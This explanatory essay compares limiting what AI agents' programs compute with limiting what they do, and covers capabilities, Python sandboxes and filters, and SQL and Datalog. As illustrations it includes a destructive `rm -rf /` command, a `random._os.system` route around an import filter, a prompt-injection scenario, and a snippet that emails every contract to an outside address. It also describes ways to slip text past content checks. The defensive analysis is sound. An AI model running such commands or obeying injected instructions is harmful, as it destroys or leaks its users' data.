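# Restricting what AI agents' programs can do versus restricting what they can compute

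## What is the difference between limiting what a program computes and limiting what it does?

An AI agent is a language model that acts on the world through software, usually over several steps. The simplest way for it to act is a tool call, in which the model asks for one predefined operation, such as looking up a customer or sending an email. The surrounding software runs the operation and returns the result to the model as text. Other agents use code actions, in which the model writes a short program that combines several operations with loops, conditions and calculation, and the software runs the whole program at once. In *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) say that, compared with tool calls, programs let the model process less text and make the agent's tool use easier for people to audit.

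Whoever builds an agent chooses the language its programs are written in. That choice affects safety because the model may misread its task or be misled by prompt injection, in which an agent follows text in the data it reads as if it were an instruction. For example, a supplier's contract might contain a line telling the reader to forward all other contracts to an outside address.

A language can restrict an AI agent's program in two ways. It can limit computation, meaning which results the program can work out, as basic SQL (the standard language for querying databases) does. Or it can limit effects, meaning what the program may do to files, networks and other systems, and leave computation general. A language that can compute less is not necessarily safer, though it is easy to confuse the two limits and assume that it is.

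### An accounts agent

For example, an agent might work in a company's accounts department. It has a table that lists each customer's parent company, a folder of contracts, and a function that sends email. Its job is to find the customers with overdue payments, trace each one to its ultimate owner, read the notice period in the contract, and email the account manager responsible. The company sets one policy, that contract text may reach only that manager.

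The steps make different demands. Finding overdue customers takes a simple filter. Tracing an owner takes repetition of unknown length, since one customer may have no parent while another sits under four holding companies, so the program has to look up each parent in turn until it reaches a row without one. With tool calls, the model would have to request each parent and read the answer before requesting the next, for every customer; a code action does the same work in a short loop. Sending the email needs hardly any computation, but it changes something outside the program. The policy concerns the route a particular piece of text takes, which a list of permitted operations would not capture.

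### Effects, pure functions and general computation

*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) defines an effect as an interaction with external state, such as reading or writing a file. Under this definition, sending the email is an effect, and so is opening the contract. A pure function computes a result and has no effects. For example, a function that takes a due date and today's date and returns the number of days between them is pure. It would not be pure if it looked up today's date on the computer's clock, because it would then be reading external state.

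A program's returned value may not show everything the program did. *Recovering Purity with Comonads and Capabilities* (2020), a paper in programming-language theory, gives two versions of a routine that applies a function to every item in a list. One works from the back of the list and the other from the front. With a pure function, the two are indistinguishable. If the function also prints each word, one version prints "right to left" and the other prints "left to right" from the same list, although both return identical lists.

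Programming languages differ in which computations they can express. A Turing-complete language can express any computation a computer can carry out, including ones that never end, and a language needs surprisingly few features to qualify. Brainfuck, one of five Turing-complete languages that Sharma and Chopra (2026) used to test language models in *EsoLang-Bench*, is deliberately awkward and has only eight commands, which operate on a strip of memory cells. Total languages, in which every program is guaranteed to finish, can't express every computation that a Turing-complete language can.

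The two scales are independent, so a program can stand high on one and low on the other:

| | Few or no effects | Wide effects |
|---|---|---|
| Limited computation | A read-only SQL query that lists overdue customers | A script with no loops that deletes every file |
| General computation | A pure function, in a general-purpose language, that follows a list of parent companies to the ultimate owner | A Python or shell program running with all of its user's permissions |

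The deleting script shows that a computationally weak language can still be unsafe. On a Unix system the script can be a single command, `rm -rf /`, with no loop, condition or arithmetic, because all the repetition happens inside the deletion program that the command starts. How much harm a language permits therefore depends on the operations it makes available, and a language with one destructive enough operation needs no other features to be dangerous. The accounts agent could likewise break its policy with one line that attaches the contracts folder to an email.

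By contrast, Zhou and colleagues describe a calculator that limits what a program does but not how complex its calculations can be. A model writes a program for each request, and the developer has declared that the program must produce an integer and do nothing else. If a hostile user asks the calculator to delete all the files on the server and then compute the factorial of 5, the model might well write a program that does both. A checker would reject that program before it runs. The programs are written in Haskell, where any operation that touches the outside world carries a mark in its type (the description of what kind of value it yields), and the mark spreads to the whole program containing it. A program that only computed the factorial would pass.

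A program with few effects can still cause harm, whether or not its computation is limited. A pure function can run forever and tie up the machine. A read-only query can return confidential rows to a model that then outputs them elsewhere.

### Where the power to act comes from

On most computers, a program gets all of its user's permissions just by running. *Robust Composition* (Miller, 2006), a doctoral thesis on how programs that do not trust one another can cooperate, illustrates this with the card game Solitaire. The game perhaps needs only the right to write one file, to save a score, yet it could also delete files, search the user's email or install a back door. Solitaire itself probably does none of this, but an attacker who takes control of it through a bug could do all of it. An agent's Python program, started in the ordinary way, is in the same position, except that its author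 is a model that has been reading strangers' documents.

Miller, Yee and Shapiro, in *Capability Myths Demolished*, call this ambient authority, meaning authority that a program exercises without selecting it. They compare it to a building with no keys, where each door opens by itself for anyone who qualifies. For example, when a program opens a file on Unix, it supplies a file name but no credential, and the system allows or refuses the request according to the permissions of the user running the program.

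The common remedy is a sandbox, which limits the files, networks and system functions a running program can reach. A sandbox for the accounts agent might expose only the customer table, the contracts folder and the mail server. It would work for a program in any language. Miller objects that some sandboxes fix the list of permissions at launch, whereas the authority a program needs changes as it runs. Twenty years later, Zhou and colleagues make much the same complaint about the operating-system sandboxes around coding agents, though they consider these a useful complement to limits in the programming language. In the accounts example, the contracts folder and the mail server both have to stay open, so the sandbox does not stop the program from sending contract text to the wrong recipient through the permitted mail server.

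A capability works differently. It is an unforgeable program value that must be held in order to perform a given effect. Miller explains it with two Unix commands that both copy a file:

- `cp foo.txt bar.txt` passes two names to the copying program, which must then open the files itself. To do that for any names it might receive, it needs authority over every file its user can reach.
- `cat < foo.txt > bar.txt` makes the command shell open the files first and hand over two open connections. The copying program needs the right to read one file and to write the other, and no more.

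On an ordinary Unix system, both commands still run with all the user's authority, but Miller is comparing the least authority each would need. For the accounts agent, the `cp` style is an email function that accepts any address. The `cat` style would be a value that can send mail only to one customer's account manager, so there is no address for an injected instruction to change.

*Early Capability Architectures* recounts that Dennis and Van Horn of MIT introduced the word "capability" in 1966, in the design of a hypothetical operating system for machines that several programs shared. Each computation had a list of capabilities, and each capability pointed to an object and stated what the computation was allowed to do with it. Miller's thesis, which Zhou and colleagues cite, applies the idea to programming languages. There, a capability is a reference that inseparably combines an object's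 name, permission to use the object and the means of using it. Code can hold a capability if it had the reference from the start, created the object, got the reference from its own creator, or received it from other code that already had access to both the recipient and the object. It cannot gain access by guessing an object's name.

A capability-restricted language allows general computation but lets a program perform only the effects it has been granted. To enforce that limit, a language must exclude several features. Miller lists forged pointers, direct access to another object's private state, and global variables that any code can alter. C++ fails because it can turn an integer into a pointer, and Java fails because of its global variables. Calculation requires none of these features. In Miller's account, what remains without them is essentially the lambda calculus, a minimal and Turing-complete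 model of computation, with some local side effects added. The restriction therefore doesn't reduce what the language can compute.

Limiting what a program does takes engineering work. *Recovering Purity* points to the standard library, the ready-made functions that come with a language. If the library offers a printing channel that any code can refer to, every program can print, whatever the rest of the language forbids. For this reason, the builders of Joe-E, a capability-restricted version of Java, undertook what the paper describes as a massive effort to rewrite Java's library. Some newer languages track capabilities in their types instead.

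Capabilities also leave a gap that matters for the accounts policy. In *Declarative Policies for Capability Control*, Dimoulas, Moore and colleagues describe a web page with a deadline planner, which may use part of the browser's storage, and an advertising component, which may not. The advertising component never holds the storage capability, but it may still affect what is stored by interacting with the planner. Controlling who holds a capability therefore doesn't control who or what influences its use. The accounts agent needs both the contract and a way to send email, so it couldn't do its job without either one. Its policy calls for information-flow control, which sets rules about where data may travel and enforces them by labelling data and checking the labels. Odersky and colleagues describe a similar problem, in which an agent must summarise changes to a set of classified contracts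 without leaking their text or letting that text steer it. They note that earlier work regarded such problems as fundamentally hard for current agents.

### Control and three meanings of "expressive"

Zhou and colleagues describe the usual dilemma as a trade-off between control and expressiveness. Fixed tools give strong control but little expressiveness, while code interpreters give the reverse. In their example, an agent compiles bibliographies and must take every entry from DBLP, a computer-science publication database. With an interpreter, the agent can search, sort and filter freely, but it can also skip the approved functions and write an invented entry straight to the file. If the interpreter is replaced with a few tools, one of which fetches an entry and writes it in a single step, the agent can't fabricate entries. But it also can't run code on the results, so the model has to inspect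 the entries one at a time to find the earliest paper.

The two options in this dilemma lie on one diagonal of the table above. Fixed tools restrict both computation and effects, while an interpreter in an ordinary sandbox leaves computation unrestricted but offers only coarse control over effects. The example doesn't show that the two must be restricted or loosened together, and Zhou and colleagues go on to argue that a typed language can separate them. "Expressiveness" also has more than one meaning, and a restriction can be severe in one sense and take nothing away in another.

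In the narrowest sense, a language's expressive power is the set of functions it can compute. In *On the Expressive Power of Programming Languages*, Felleisen rejects this as a way to compare most languages, because most are Turing-complete and can therefore compute the same functions. It does distinguish basic SQL from Python, which matters when the accounts agent has to follow an ownership chain of unknown length, because basic SQL can't do that. Felleisen proposes a finer measure, under which a feature adds expressive power if removing it would require a global reorganisation of the programs that use it. A "repeat until" loop adds none to a language that already has "while", since a programmer can replace one with the other without changing the rest of the program. Removing a feature such as assignment, which changes the value a name stands for, can force a programmer to rewrite large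 parts of a program.

A user is more likely to care about which tasks an agent can finish. Computing power does not guarantee that an agent can finish a task, because a pure language can be fully general and still be unable to send an email. Miller similarly observes that a version of Solitaire with virtually no authority could not save its score to a file. An agent with modest computing power and the right few operations may finish everything its owner asks. Benchmarks measure utility as the share of legitimate tasks an agent completes, which depends on the model and its tools as well as the language.

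The remaining sense is how easily a model can write the program. Sharma and Chopra gave five models the same 80 short programming problems in different languages. The best models solved all of them in Python or JavaScript. In five esoteric languages, which can all in principle express the same solutions, the best scores ranged from about 0 to 11 percent, even when the models could see error messages and try again. The gap probably overstates how much a sensible restricted language would lower scores, because these languages are both deliberately hard to use and much less familiar to models. Python has between 340 and more than 60,000 times as many public GitHub repositories as these languages do.

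*Frontier Coding Agents Use Metaprogramming to Adapt to Unfamiliar Programming Languages* (Sharma, Thorat and Chopra, 2026), a follow-up, shows how much the surrounding tools matter. The agents could edit files and run code while they worked. OpenAI's GPT-5.4, at a high reasoning setting, now solved 79 of the 80 problems in Brainfuck, and Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6 solved 64. Mostly they wrote Python programs that generated the Brainfuck code, then debugged the Python. On one problem, Opus first wrote 1,884 bytes of Brainfuck by hand and failed, then wrote a generator whose 24,500 bytes of output passed every test. When Sharma and colleagues banned generators, the two agents solved 27 and 29 problems. JavaScript and Rust worked nearly as well as Python for writing the generators, so the advantage came from having a familiar general-purpose language available.

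Weaker agents could gain some of that advantage from a small library of working generator code, but a written description of the strategy hardly helped them. With the library, Claude Sonnet 4.6 went from solving 12 Brainfuck problems to 64, GPT-5.4 mini from 5 to 53, and Claude Haiku 4.5 only from 4 to 7. Designers of a restricted language for agents can therefore offset much of the added difficulty by supplying helper code, at least for models strong enough to use it. But if agents write their own generators in Python, that code has to run somewhere, and the restricted language doesn't control what Python can reach there.

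## Why do agents write Python, and what holds a Python program back?

Agents that act through code usually write Python or JavaScript. Neither language by itself limits what a program can compute or what effects it can have. Developers chose these languages because models write them well, and have had to add limits afterwards.

### Why code replaced single tool calls

To make a tool call, a model outputs a special marker followed by a short structured message, usually in the JSON format, that names an operation and its inputs. *Code Mode*, an article by Varda and Pai from the internet infrastructure company Cloudflare, points out that these markers never occur in ordinary text, so developers have to train models on invented examples. But the models' training data also includes real code from millions of open-source projects.

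Tool calls also send every intermediate result through the model. Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP* (MCP is the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for connecting agents to tools) gives the example of an agent that downloads a meeting transcript and attaches it to a sales record. The model has to read the transcript as the result of one call and then write it out as the input to the next. For a two-hour meeting, that could mean processing an extra 50,000 tokens (the word fragments that models read and write), and the model may make copying mistakes. A program can keep the transcript in a variable, and the model sees only what the program prints. Loops save further requests, as in the accounts agent's search for parent companies.

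Wang, Chen and colleagues tested this idea, which they called CodeAct, in *Executable Code Actions Elicit Better LLM Agents* (2024). They gave 17 models the same tools and had them act in Python, in JSON or in a fixed text format. The main test had 82 tasks in areas such as finance, travel planning and web browsing, most of which needed several tools. A model had ten turns to produce an answer that exactly matched the correct one. The best model, a preview version of GPT-4, solved 74.4 percent of the tasks with Python, 53.7 percent with text and 52.4 percent with JSON. It also needed about two fewer turns with Python.

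Python was the best format, or tied for best, for 12 of the 17 models, all of which are now long out of date. But when the task was to make one correct call, the same GPT-4 model did better with JSON (82.7 percent) than with Python (76.7 percent). So Python's advantage on the longer tasks probably came from combining operations, not from the model knowing Python better than JSON. The weaker models gained little, and no open-weight model solved more than 16 percent of the longer tasks in any format.

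More recent evidence is mostly about token use. Varda and Pai report that agents can handle more tools, and more complex ones, when they write code, but give no success rates. In Anthropic's example, an agent that reads tool descriptions from files as it needs them uses 2,000 tokens instead of 150,000. Carey, in *Code Mode*, a 2026 follow-up to the Cloudflare article, describes a server that offers more than 2,500 operations through two functions, one to search for operations and one to run code. Describing the two functions takes about 1,000 tokens, whereas describing every operation as a separate tool would take 1.17 million. An agent can achieve part of this reduction without code actions by searching for relevant tools and calling them one at a time.

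Writing a program brings a modest gain on a small task. When Pydantic, a company that makes tools for Python developers, asked Claude Sonnet 4.5 to compare the weather in London and Paris, writing a program cut requests to the model from four to two, the time from 12.2 seconds to 9.1, and the cost from 1.9 cents to 1.7. The savings grow with the number of tools and the amount of data. Cloudflare now turns the method on by default in its gateways for agent tools, according to its *Code mode for MCP server portals* (2026).

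Cloudflare's agents write JavaScript or TypeScript, so most of these arguments apply to any familiar general-purpose language. Wang and colleagues chose Python because it is popular and has many ready-made packages.

### The accounts task in Python

The accounts agent might write the following program, using a company module called `accounts`. The helper `notice_period` searches a contract for the relevant clause.

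```python
from accounts import crm, mail, notice_period                # A
from pathlib import Path

parent = {c.id: c.parent_id for c in crm.customers()}        # B

for c in crm.overdue_customers():
    owner = c.id
    while parent[owner] is not None:
        owner = parent[owner]
    text = Path("contracts", f"{c.id}.txt").read_text()      # C
    notice = notice_period(text)                             # D
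    mail.send(c.manager_email,                               # E
              f"{c.name}, owned by {owner}: {notice}")
    print(c.name, "done")                                    # F
```

This program obeys the company's policy on contract text. However, a small change at any of the marked lines could break it, and ordinary Python would run the altered version just as readily:

- **A:** The program can import any installed module, including modules that open network connections or start other programs. It could send out contracts without using the mail function at all.
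- **B:** The program can do whatever the database login allows. If that includes changing records, it could replace a manager's address with an outsider's, and line E would then send the text to the wrong person without any change of its own.
- **C:** The program can open any file its user can open. It could read every contract, or copy them all to a shared folder.
- **D:** Nothing in Python marks a function as pure, so a helper that appears only to search the text could also send it somewhere.
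- **E:** The mail function accepts any address and any text.
- **F:** Whatever the program prints goes back to the model. Printing a contract would put it in the model's context and, if another company hosts the model, on that company's servers.

Lines A to D are dangerous because of ambient authority. But the agent needs to send email and report its progress, so lines E and F would remain available even if the program had no other powers.

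Writing code offers some protection against prompt injection. The model writes this program before it has read any contract, so an instruction hidden in a contract can't influence it. But that protection may not last, because if `notice_period` finds nothing in an oddly worded contract, the model will probably print the text to see what went wrong. Any instruction the supplier hid there could then influence the next program it writes.

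### Filtering the program

One way to restrict a Python program is to check each operation as it runs. Smolagents, Hugging Face's library for building agents, does this. By default, it runs the model's code on the user's own machine. According to Hugging Face's *Secure code execution*, smolagents first parses the program into a syntax tree, which shows how the statements and expressions fit together. It then works through the tree one operation at a time and raises an error if it has no rule for an operation. The program can import only modules on a list, which initially contains harmless ones such as `math` and `datetime`. A `while` loop stops with an error after a million iterations, which would keep the accounts program from looping forever if two companies were each recorded as the other's parent.

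The filter would reject the accounts program at its first line, because `accounts` is not on the list. A developer could add both it and `pathlib`, the module that opens the contracts, but `pathlib` can open other files too. The security firm NCC Group advises against extending the list this way. It recommends that generated Python do only logic, arithmetic and text handling, and that developers write narrow tools for everything else.

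Filtering is difficult because harmless-looking modules can give access to dangerous ones. Python's `random` module, for example, imports `os`, so a program can run shell commands by calling `random._os.system(...)` without importing `os` itself. The smolagents filter blocks this route, and Hugging Face later added a check on every value an operation returns. But a permitted package can still do damage through its normal functions. Hugging Face gives the example of a program that uses Pillow, an image library, to save thousands of pictures until the disk is full.

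Hugging Face once presented the filter as a first layer of security. Its current reference page, *Python code executors*, says the filter "is not a security sandbox" and tells developers to run untrusted code elsewhere. This advice is sensible, since NVD's *CVE-2025-5120 Detail*, an entry in the US government's vulnerability database, records an escape from an earlier version.

### Enclosing the whole process

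A developer can instead leave Python as it is and put a barrier around the running program. A container, such as one made with Docker, gives the program its own view of files, processes and the network. Hugging Face's sample Docker set-up runs the agent as a user with few privileges and limits it to 512 megabytes of memory and 100 processes. Inside the container, the program can use any Python package.

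If the agent stays outside and sends only its generated code to a remote sandbox, its credentials stay outside too. But then the code can't start a helper agent, because the helper would have no credentials for calling a model. Hugging Face's solution is to run the whole agent inside the sandbox and pass in an access token, which puts the token in the same sandbox as the generated code. Returning results from the sandbox is also risky, because pickle, Python's usual format for storing objects, can run arbitrary code when another program loads it. By default, smolagents therefore accepts results only in a safer format.

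Web browsers offer another model for this kind of barrier because they run untrusted code on almost every page they load, as Willison observes in *Running Python code in a sandbox with MicroPython and WASM*. WebAssembly is a compact instruction format that browsers and other software can run in an enclosed environment. If a developer compiles a Python interpreter to WebAssembly, the interpreter and its programs can reach the outside world only through functions that the host supplies. Willison thinks a sandbox isn't much use unless it can expose selected functions to the code inside it.

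Cloudflare runs its agents' JavaScript in isolates, small separate instances of the engine that the Chrome browser uses. An isolate starts in a few milliseconds, so Cloudflare can create a new one for each program and then throw it away. In Varda and Pai's design, the usual network functions raise errors. The program instead receives objects called bindings, each connected to one tool server. A supervisor outside the isolate holds the access keys and adds them to the requests, so the program cannot leak them.

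A binding works much like a capability, but it can be very broad. In the server Carey describes, the program gets a single `cloudflare.request()` function that can request any of the 2,500 operations. The permissions the user approved when connecting determine which of these the program may carry out. An agent that needs to change one firewall rule may therefore be able to change the others too.

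All these barriers are too coarse. A sandbox that exposed only the contracts folder, the database and the mail server would deal with much of lines A to C. But it doesn't represent customers or account managers, so it can't match a contract to the person who is allowed to receive it.

### Running a vetted subset of Python

*STELP* (Shinde, Wadhwa and colleagues, 2026) describes a system from the bank Capital One that lets developers restrict Python itself. A developer lists the parts of the language, the packages and the tools that a program may use. STELP parses the program and rejects it if the syntax tree contains anything else. It then translates the program into a version with added checks and runs it one statement at a time. Calls to tools go through a separate service with time limits. If STELP blocks a program, a second model explains why so that the model that wrote the program can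 revise it.

The developer can limit computation as well as effects this way, for example by leaving out `while` loops or capping how deeply loops may nest. Without `while`, the program above could no longer follow chains of ownership the way it does, but it could still email every contract to a stranger.

To test STELP, Shinde and colleagues took correct solutions to 164 short programming exercises and had a model insert 12 kinds of flaw, such as infinite loops and attempts to read system files. After human reviewers removed the faulty samples, 470 unsafe programs remained. STELP blocked all of them and allowed 98.1 percent of the safe programs. CodeShield, a scanner from Meta that looks for known dangerous patterns, blocked 68 percent of the unsafe programs and allowed 93 percent of the safe ones.

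These results are weak evidence of how STELP would perform in an office. Shinde and colleagues limited its list of permissions to the minimum that the safe programs in the test needed. The exercises are small puzzles, so a list fitted to them can leave out nearly everything dangerous, and most of the blocked programs did contain a call or import that was not on the list. The accounts agent has to read files and send email, so its list would have to allow both. The inserted flaws were also common programming hazards, whereas a real attacker would look for weaknesses in STELP itself. The test does support the conclusion that a short list works well when the task needs few permissions. The median delay was small, at 0.19 milliseconds.

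### Starting with nothing

Pydantic argues that containers work backwards, because the developer starts with a complete system and then tries to remove everything dangerous. Its alternative, Monty, is a new Python interpreter with no operation for opening a file or a network connection. A program running in Monty can affect the outside world only through what the developer supplies.

When a program calls a function the developer has supplied, such as `get_price`, Monty pauses and passes the function's name and inputs to the host, the software that started it. The host runs the real function and returns the result, and the program continues. According to Pydantic's *Security Model*, a developer can also attach folders or expose chosen parts of the host's own objects. For instance, a program might receive an account object that lets it withdraw money but not close the account. By default the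 program can also read the clock and get random numbers, but the developer can turn both off.

For the accounts agent, a developer could attach the contracts folder as read-only and supply functions for looking up customers and sending email. The program could not then import a networking module, change a customer record or open a file outside the folder. This removes the ambient authority that lines A to D rely on, but the program can still run any loop or calculation.

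The drawback is that Monty supports only part of Python, which Pydantic's *Limitations* explains is deliberate, since it implements just enough of the language for a model to express a task. Early versions had no classes, which programmers use to define their own kinds of object, but Pydantic's *Classes* shows that simple ones now work. Programs still can't load third-party packages such as Pillow. A developer can offer parts of a package through host functions, as Pydantic did with a library for reading web pages, but must write and check each function.

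Monty is also fast. Pydantic's *Monty* reports that obtaining a sandbox and running ten commands takes 1.2 milliseconds, compared with 900 for a local Docker container and 1,900 for a remote sandbox service. The test conditions favour Monty because it uses workers that are already running and keeps its state between commands, while the others start from scratch and repeat the earlier commands each time.

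Developers are responsible for whatever they supply to Monty, which Pydantic says "cannot guarantee that what you handed it is safe". Host functions run with the full authority of the host, so one that fetches any web address gives the program access to the whole internet. The interpreter itself also carries risks. Monty reuses each worker for up to 1,000 sessions by default, so an attacker who took over a worker could see the sessions that followed. Pydantic therefore recommends a fresh worker for each session when the users don't trust one another. It also combines the restricted interpreter with a process sandbox, running the workers as separate processes without access to the host's environment variables, where programs often keep passwords. Its commercial version adds operating-system isolation.

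### Why a sandbox can't express the accounts policy

Suppose the accounts agent runs in Monty with only three functions: one that lists overdue customers, one that reads a contract and one that sends email. After reading a contract with a hidden instruction, the model writes this:

```python
for c in overdue_customers():
    send_email("audit@supplier.example", read_contract(c.id))
```

Monty would run the program because the developer granted all three functions. The smolagents filter would allow it because it has no forbidden import, STELP because it uses only approved tools, and a container because it connects to the permitted mail server. None of these systems has a rule about the flow of text from the contract to the email, which is where the breach occurs. Odersky and colleagues raise the same objection to lists of permitted commands and to prompts that ask the user to approve each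 action, since an agent can read a secret in one permitted step and send it out in a later one.

Narrower functions restrict the program further. If the mail function looked up the manager's address itself, the program could no longer email an outsider, but it could still send one customer's contract to another customer's manager. A single function that reads a contract, extracts the notice period and emails it to the right person would prevent that too, but the developer would again have to write a fixed tool for each task.

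The mail function could also compare each message with the contracts and refuse any that match. This would catch a careless mistake, but a program with general computation could easily evade the check by reversing the text, encoding it as numbers or spreading it over several messages.

Anthropic describes a more promising method for personal details. The software that connects the agent to its tools replaces email addresses and phone numbers with placeholders before the model sees them, then restores the real values when the agent passes them to another tool. Anthropic suggests that developers could use the same mechanism to control where data goes. To enforce the accounts policy, the software would need to track which contract a piece of text came from, even after the program had cut it up or rewritten it. An ordinary Python string doesn't record its source, but CaMeL, an interpreter designed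 for agents, does this by attaching labels to values as the program runs.

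## What can an agent do in SQL, and what can it not do?

A developer can also start with a smaller language than Python. Basic SQL has no loops and can't open a file or contact a server. Much of the data an office agent needs is already in databases that accept SQL. But the language has grown well beyond its basic form, and it includes commands that delete data. What an SQL agent can do therefore depends on which parts of the language it may use and on the permissions of its database account.

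### What a basic query computes

A basic query builds one table out of others. If the accounts agent's company also keeps its invoices in the database, this query works out how much each account manager's customers owe in late payments:

```sql
SELECT c.manager_email, SUM(i.amount) AS owed
FROM customers AS c
JOIN invoices AS i ON i.customer_id = c.id
WHERE i.paid = FALSE AND i.due_date < CURRENT_DATE
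GROUP BY c.manager_email;
```

`JOIN` matches each invoice to its customer, and `WHERE` keeps unpaid invoices past their due date. `GROUP BY` collects the rows that share a manager, `SUM` totals each group, and `SELECT` chooses the columns to return. Apart from grouping and totals, all of this belongs to relational algebra, a small set of operations that each take one or two tables and produce a new one.

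The query describes a result, and a part of the database called the planner chooses the steps. It might discard the paid invoices first and then match the few that remain, or it might use an index to go straight to the late ones. The planner can choose because each operation has a fixed meaning, so the rules of the algebra guarantee the same answer either way. A Python loop that calls `notice_period` has no such guarantee, because the function might do anything.

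Fixed meanings also help with safety, because software can determine which tables a basic query touches before running it. Every basic query also eventually finishes. If it refers to *k* tables of at most *n* rows each, the database has to check at most *n*<sup>*k*</sup> combinations of rows, though a large join can still take too long to be practical.

### Following a chain of owners

The accounts agent's search for ultimate owners is hard to write in basic SQL. Each row of the `companies` table gives a company and its parent. Joining the table to itself once gives the parent's parent, and each further join follows one more link. Three joins reach the fourth holding company above a customer. If someone then inserts a fifth, the query returns the wrong owner without any error.

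No combination of the same operations avoids the problem. Aho and Ullman showed in 1979 that relational algebra can't express transitive closure, according to Immerman's *Relational Queries Computable in Polynomial Time*. Here, transitive closure means the list of all pairs in which one company sits anywhere above another. A very long ownership chain illustrates why. Two companies in the middle can be far from each other and from both ends. A fixed query can examine only a limited number of links around each company, and within that range the two look identical, so the query can't determine which one owns the other.

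The result matters only when the chains have no known maximum length. If the company knows that none has more than ten links, ten joins are enough. The result also applies only to a single query, not to the agent as a whole. An agent that can run a query, read the answer and run another can follow the chain one link at a time, because the model supplies the loop. But that brings back the slow exchange of tool calls and results that code actions were meant to avoid.

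Since 1999, the SQL standard has had a better answer, the recursive query:

```sql
WITH RECURSIVE owners (customer, company) AS (
    SELECT id, id FROM companies
  UNION
    SELECT o.customer, c.parent_id
    FROM owners AS o
    JOIN companies AS c ON c.id = o.company
    WHERE c.parent_id IS NOT NULL
)
SELECT o.customer, o.company AS ultimate_owner
FROM owners AS o
JOIN companies AS c ON c.id = o.company
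WHERE c.parent_id IS NULL;
```

The part before `UNION` is the base case, which pairs every company with itself. The part after it is the recursive step, which adds the parent of each company found so far. *Compiling Linear Datalog to SQL for Program Analysis* (2026) explains that modern databases run this step repeatedly, each time on only the rows the previous round added, until a round adds nothing new. A customer under four holding companies needs four rounds, and a fifth finds no more parents. The last four lines keep only the owners that have no parent.

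This query is safer than the Python version in one respect. If two companies were each recorded as the other's parent, the Python loop would run forever, but the query would stop once it found no new rows, because `UNION` discards duplicates. The query would lose that protection if the agent added a column that counts the links, because each trip around the circle would produce a new row with a higher number. *Language-Integrated Recursive Queries (Full Version)* (2025) attributes this problem to operations such as addition and joining strings, which can create values that were not in the database. Some products, including SQL Server and Oracle, require `UNION ALL`, which keeps duplicates, and offer other ways of catching endless recursion.

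Recursion and arithmetic together make SQL Turing-complete. The PostgreSQL wiki's *Cyclic Tag System* demonstrates this with a single query by Andrew Gierth that uses only standard SQL. The query runs a cyclic tag system, which keeps a string of ones and zeros and a list of pieces, in this case 110, 01 and 0000. At each step, the system removes the first digit of the string, adds the current piece to the end if that digit was a 1, and moves to the next piece. Starting from 1, the string becomes 110, then 1001, then 0010000. Mathematicians have proved that such a system can carry out any computation, given the right pieces.

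SQL is a restricted language only if someone has chosen a restricted subset of it. Salihoğlu's university lecture *Recursion in SQL & (optional) Datalog* (2025) lists "not Turing-complete" among SQL's limitations, but this refers to the SQL his students had seen before he introduced recursion. An agent connected to an ordinary modern database can use the whole language unless the developer prevents it.

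### Datalog as a middle point

Datalog is a query language that includes recursion but, in its plain form, no arithmetic. It expresses the search for owners in two rules, where `:-` means "if":

```prolog
owner(X, Y) :- parent(X, Y).
owner(X, Z) :- owner(X, Y), parent(Y, Z).
```

A recursive rule can define a company's owners as its parent and the parent of any owner already found. Plain Datalog can only rearrange values that are in the data. With *n* different values, a table of *k* columns has at most *n*<sup>*k*</sup> possible rows, so every program eventually runs out of rows to add and stops, which makes plain Datalog a total language. Unrestricted arithmetic on whole numbers would remove the guarantee that every program stops, as it does in SQL.

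Plain Datalog also lacks negation, so unlike basic SQL, it can't find the customers who have *no* late invoices. Most practical versions add a controlled form of negation. If the data also has an order, such as alphabetical order, Datalog with negation can express exactly the yes-or-no questions about a database that a computer can answer in polynomial time. Polynomial time means that the work grows no faster than some fixed power of the amount of data. Immerman proved the corresponding result for relational calculus, the logical counterpart of relational algebra, with an added operator for recursion.

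Recursive queries can compute a surprising amount without arithmetic. *GQL and SQL/PGQ* (2024), a study of languages for querying networks of linked records, uses one to test whether the length of a chain is a power of two. The query first builds a table of all positions *i*, *j* and *k* on the chain for which *i* + *j* = *k*, which lets it add only up to the length of the chain. But Datalog without arithmetic could not total a customer's invoices or compose the text of an email, because the total and the text would be new values.

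Developers who want an agent to write Datalog may not need a new database. Recursive SQL corresponds to linear Datalog, in which each rule may refer only once to the table it defines. *Compiling Linear Datalog to SQL for Program Analysis* presents a translator from linear Datalog to ordinary recursive SQL queries.

### The accounts task, step by step

SQL covers the accounts agent's work unevenly:

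| Step | What it requires |
|---|---|
| Find customers with overdue payments | Basic SQL |
| Look up each customer's account manager | Basic SQL |
| Trace each customer to its ultimate owner | A recursive query, or one basic query per link |
| Fetch the contract | Basic SQL if the text is in the database, otherwise a tool that reads files |
| Find the notice period | Pattern matching for standard wording, a language model for the rest |
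| Email the account manager | A tool outside SQL |

Only the ownership search needs more computation than basic SQL offers. Sending the email needs a separate tool because the query language itself cannot write files or contact servers, though some databases add functions that do.

Finding the notice period is hard because contracts word it in different ways. SQL can search for "notice period of 30 days", but a contract may instead let either party leave "at the end of the quarter following written notification". Python has better tools for matching text, but neither language can interpret that wording.

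For *Can AI Agents Answer Your Data Questions?*, Ma, Shankar and colleagues (2026) interviewed six companies building data agents, then wrote 104 questions over 17 datasets, each spread across at least two databases. The agents could use both database queries and Python. The best agent, OpenAI's GPT-5.5 running in Codex, answered 57 percent of the questions correctly on a single attempt. Answering 84 percent of the questions required extracting values from free text, which the agents almost always attempted with regular expressions (patterns for matching characters). No agent correctly answered any of the questions about patents, where dates took forms such as "March the 18th, 2019". In medical records, one pattern for "MALE" also matched "FEMALE".

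### Calling a model from inside a query

Some databases let a query call a language model on each row. With a function named, say, `ask_model`, the accounts agent could write:

```sql
SELECT customer_id,
       ask_model('How many days of notice?', contract_text)
FROM contracts;
```

*Text2SQL is Not Enough* (Biswal, Patel and colleagues, 2024) gives the example of a request to summarise the reviews of the highest-grossing romantic film considered a classic. SQL can select the romances and sort them by revenue, while a language model can identify the classics from their titles. Google's BigQuery ML and Microsoft's Predictive SQL build machine-learning functions into queries. Other systems provide semantic operators, which filter, rank or summarise rows according to a description in plain English.

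To test the approach, Biswal and colleagues rewrote 80 questions from an existing SQL benchmark so that the database alone could not answer them. Some required outside knowledge, such as which players are taller than Stephen Curry, and others required judgement, such as which comments are the most sarcastic. On the 60 questions they scored automatically, Llama 3.1, a model from Meta, answered 17 percent correctly by writing SQL, and 13 percent when it used SQL to fetch rows and then read them all at once. Programs that called the same model row by row answered 55 percent correctly. But experts who knew the data wrote those programs by hand, so the result shows how much model calls can add, not how well an agent would use them.

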